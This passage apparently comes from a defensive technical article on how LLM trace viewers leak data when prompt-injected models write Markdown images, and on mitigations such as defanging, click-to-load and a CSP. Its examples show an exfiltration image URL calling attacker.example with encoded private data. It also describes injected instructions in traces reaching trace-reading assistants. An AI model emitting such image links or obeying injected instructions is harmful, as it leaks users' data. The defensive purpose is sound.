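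Two years later, the same tool added compact tags that replace media addresses in its JSON views, so that a reader can open the media without leaving the page (Wochinger, 2026, *Preview media in JSON views*). The announcement doesn't cover security or whether the browser requests anything before the reader opens a tag. If the browser requests nothing until then, a reader who stays in those views avoids a leak that the formatted trace page would allow.

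LangChain's *Log multimodal traces* covers pictures that an app passes to a model as part of a question, not Markdown images in the model's answers. A picture in a question is usually less dangerous because the user or the app chose its address. But an agent's trace contains many model calls, and the answer from one call often becomes part of the next question, so an address that the model wrote can appear among the inputs.

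Phoenix, a trace tool that companies run on their own servers, has the most detailed advice on network security. Arize's *Network Security* recommends letting the Phoenix server contact only the services it needs, and lists "a malicious payload in a trace" among the ways an attacker might take over that server. This protects the server well, but if the viewer displays an outside image, the reader's browser requests it, and the server's rule doesn't affect that request. Phoenix also has a setting that turns off outside resources, but Arize describes it as covering requests that Phoenix makes for itself, such as loading fonts.

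None of these pages describes a leak, and a tool may have protections that its documentation omits. But a company can't conclude from any of them that its viewer is safe.

Customers also press the makers to show more pictures. In *GenAI experiment tracing does not render markdown images* (juandados), a customer of the data company Databricks complained that its trace viewer failed to display pictures that LangSmith displayed, and was avoiding the tool for that reason. These pictures were embedded in the Markdown as Base64, so the browser doesn't contact a server to display them. A viewer can therefore display them and still block every outside image.

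### Cleaning before storage or in the viewer

If an app sends its own traces to a tool such as Langfuse, it can clean the text before sending it. This protects every program that later opens the trace, including ones that don't exist yet. LangSmith users, for example, can share a trace through a public link, put it in a queue for reviewers to score, or copy it into a dataset, a collection of saved examples for testing later versions. An image address in the trace stays in each copy, as it does in a saved report.

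However, cleaning has to cover every route into storage. GitLab's *Advisories for Pypi/Langsmith package* lists a flaw in LangSmith's developer kit that let streamed text bypass redaction. Cleaning also does nothing for traces stored before the company added the filter. On OpenAI's platform, the developer can choose whether OpenAI stores the answer but can't clean it first.

Deleting the image has a cost of its own. Someone who investigates an attack needs to know where the data would have gone and whose it was, and the address may be the only record of both. The software can keep the address but write it so that programs no longer recognise it, a habit security analysts call defanging:

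```
![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=QW5u...)       written by the model
[image: hxxps://attacker[.]example/logo.png?q=QW5u...]     stored in the trace
```

An investigator can still decode the part after the question mark and find Ann's note. The stored text is no longer an exact copy, so a company that may need one as evidence should keep the original in a separate file that only a few people can open, and only in a plain text editor. The trace still contains the private data. Masking that data is a separate task, and Langfuse added a feature for doing it in Python programs in June 2026.

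A control in the log viewer acts when text is displayed, so it also covers old traces and text that a filter missed. The simplest one is to show raw text by default. One programmer in the Hacker News discussion saw no reason for a log viewer to load images, since people open logs to read exactly what the model wrote. Raw text is also better evidence because it shows the address of a one-pixel image that formatting would hide.

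Some teams do need pictures, for example if their app analyses photographs. Their viewer can put a placeholder where each outside image would be and load the image only on a click:

```
Outside image, not loaded
Address: https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=QW5u...
[Load this image]
```

PromptArmor gives similar advice for chat windows. The advice suits a log viewer better, since a developer who has opened a flagged answer is already looking for something wrong and can read a web address. The viewer shouldn't offer a button that loads every image at once. It should also instruct the browser not to tell the image's server which website the image appears on, as browsers normally do. Otherwise, if a company runs its own log viewer, an attacker would learn the viewer's address.

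A CSP enforces the rule if the placeholder code has a fault. A company that runs its own viewer can usually add one at the server in front of it:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' data: https://trace-media.example.com
```

The word `data:` permits embedded pictures. The last entry is the company's own file storage. Langfuse, for example, has the browser fetch uploaded media directly from there. The entry should name that one store, not the storage provider's whole domain, because an attacker could rent space on that domain, as Rehberger did to get data out of ChatGPT. If the tool already sends a policy, the browser enforces both, so adding this one can only make the rules stricter. This policy would also stop outside images from loading on a click, so a team that wants click-to-load has to accept a looser policy or open the picture in a separate, isolated window.

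Securing the viewer should come first, because that protects everything already in storage. Cleaning traces before storage is worth adding when they leave the viewer through shared links, exports or datasets. A company that uses a hosted tool can clean its own traces but has to ask the tool's maker to secure the viewer.

Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) suggests restricting access to the logs until OpenAI responds, and examining flagged conversations in an isolated environment that can't make outside requests. Restricting access helps less, because whoever investigates flagged answers still needs it, and the data leaks if even one browser loads the image. An isolated computer that can reach only the log service stops the leak, provided the service doesn't fetch the images on its own servers.

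To test the server logs, the developer has the app produce the test image, lets the app block it, and then opens the trace. The test should cover the formatted view, the raw view, the reviewers' queue and a shared link, because a single tool can have different displays. Langfuse's documentation describes several, and LangChain's *LangSmith Cloud changelog* announced in autumn 2026 that reviewers can switch between two views of a trace while scoring it.

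### Assistants that read the traces

Trace tools now have their own assistants. In June 2026 Langfuse released Halo, which answers questions about a company's traces, and LangSmith has a chat that can open full traces. LangSmith also lets outside agents request complete inputs and outputs through the Model Context Protocol.

A defanged image is harmless to a browser, but the hostile instructions that produced it are still in the trace. When a developer asks the assistant why some answers were flagged, it reads those instructions, possibly alongside many other customers' records. An attack aimed at one customer's review could then reach far more people's data. Nobody appears to have demonstrated this against Halo or LangSmith's chat. Their makers can prevent leaks through images by blocking outside images in the assistant's answers. A company that connects its own agent to its traces should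 do the same wherever that agent's answers appear.
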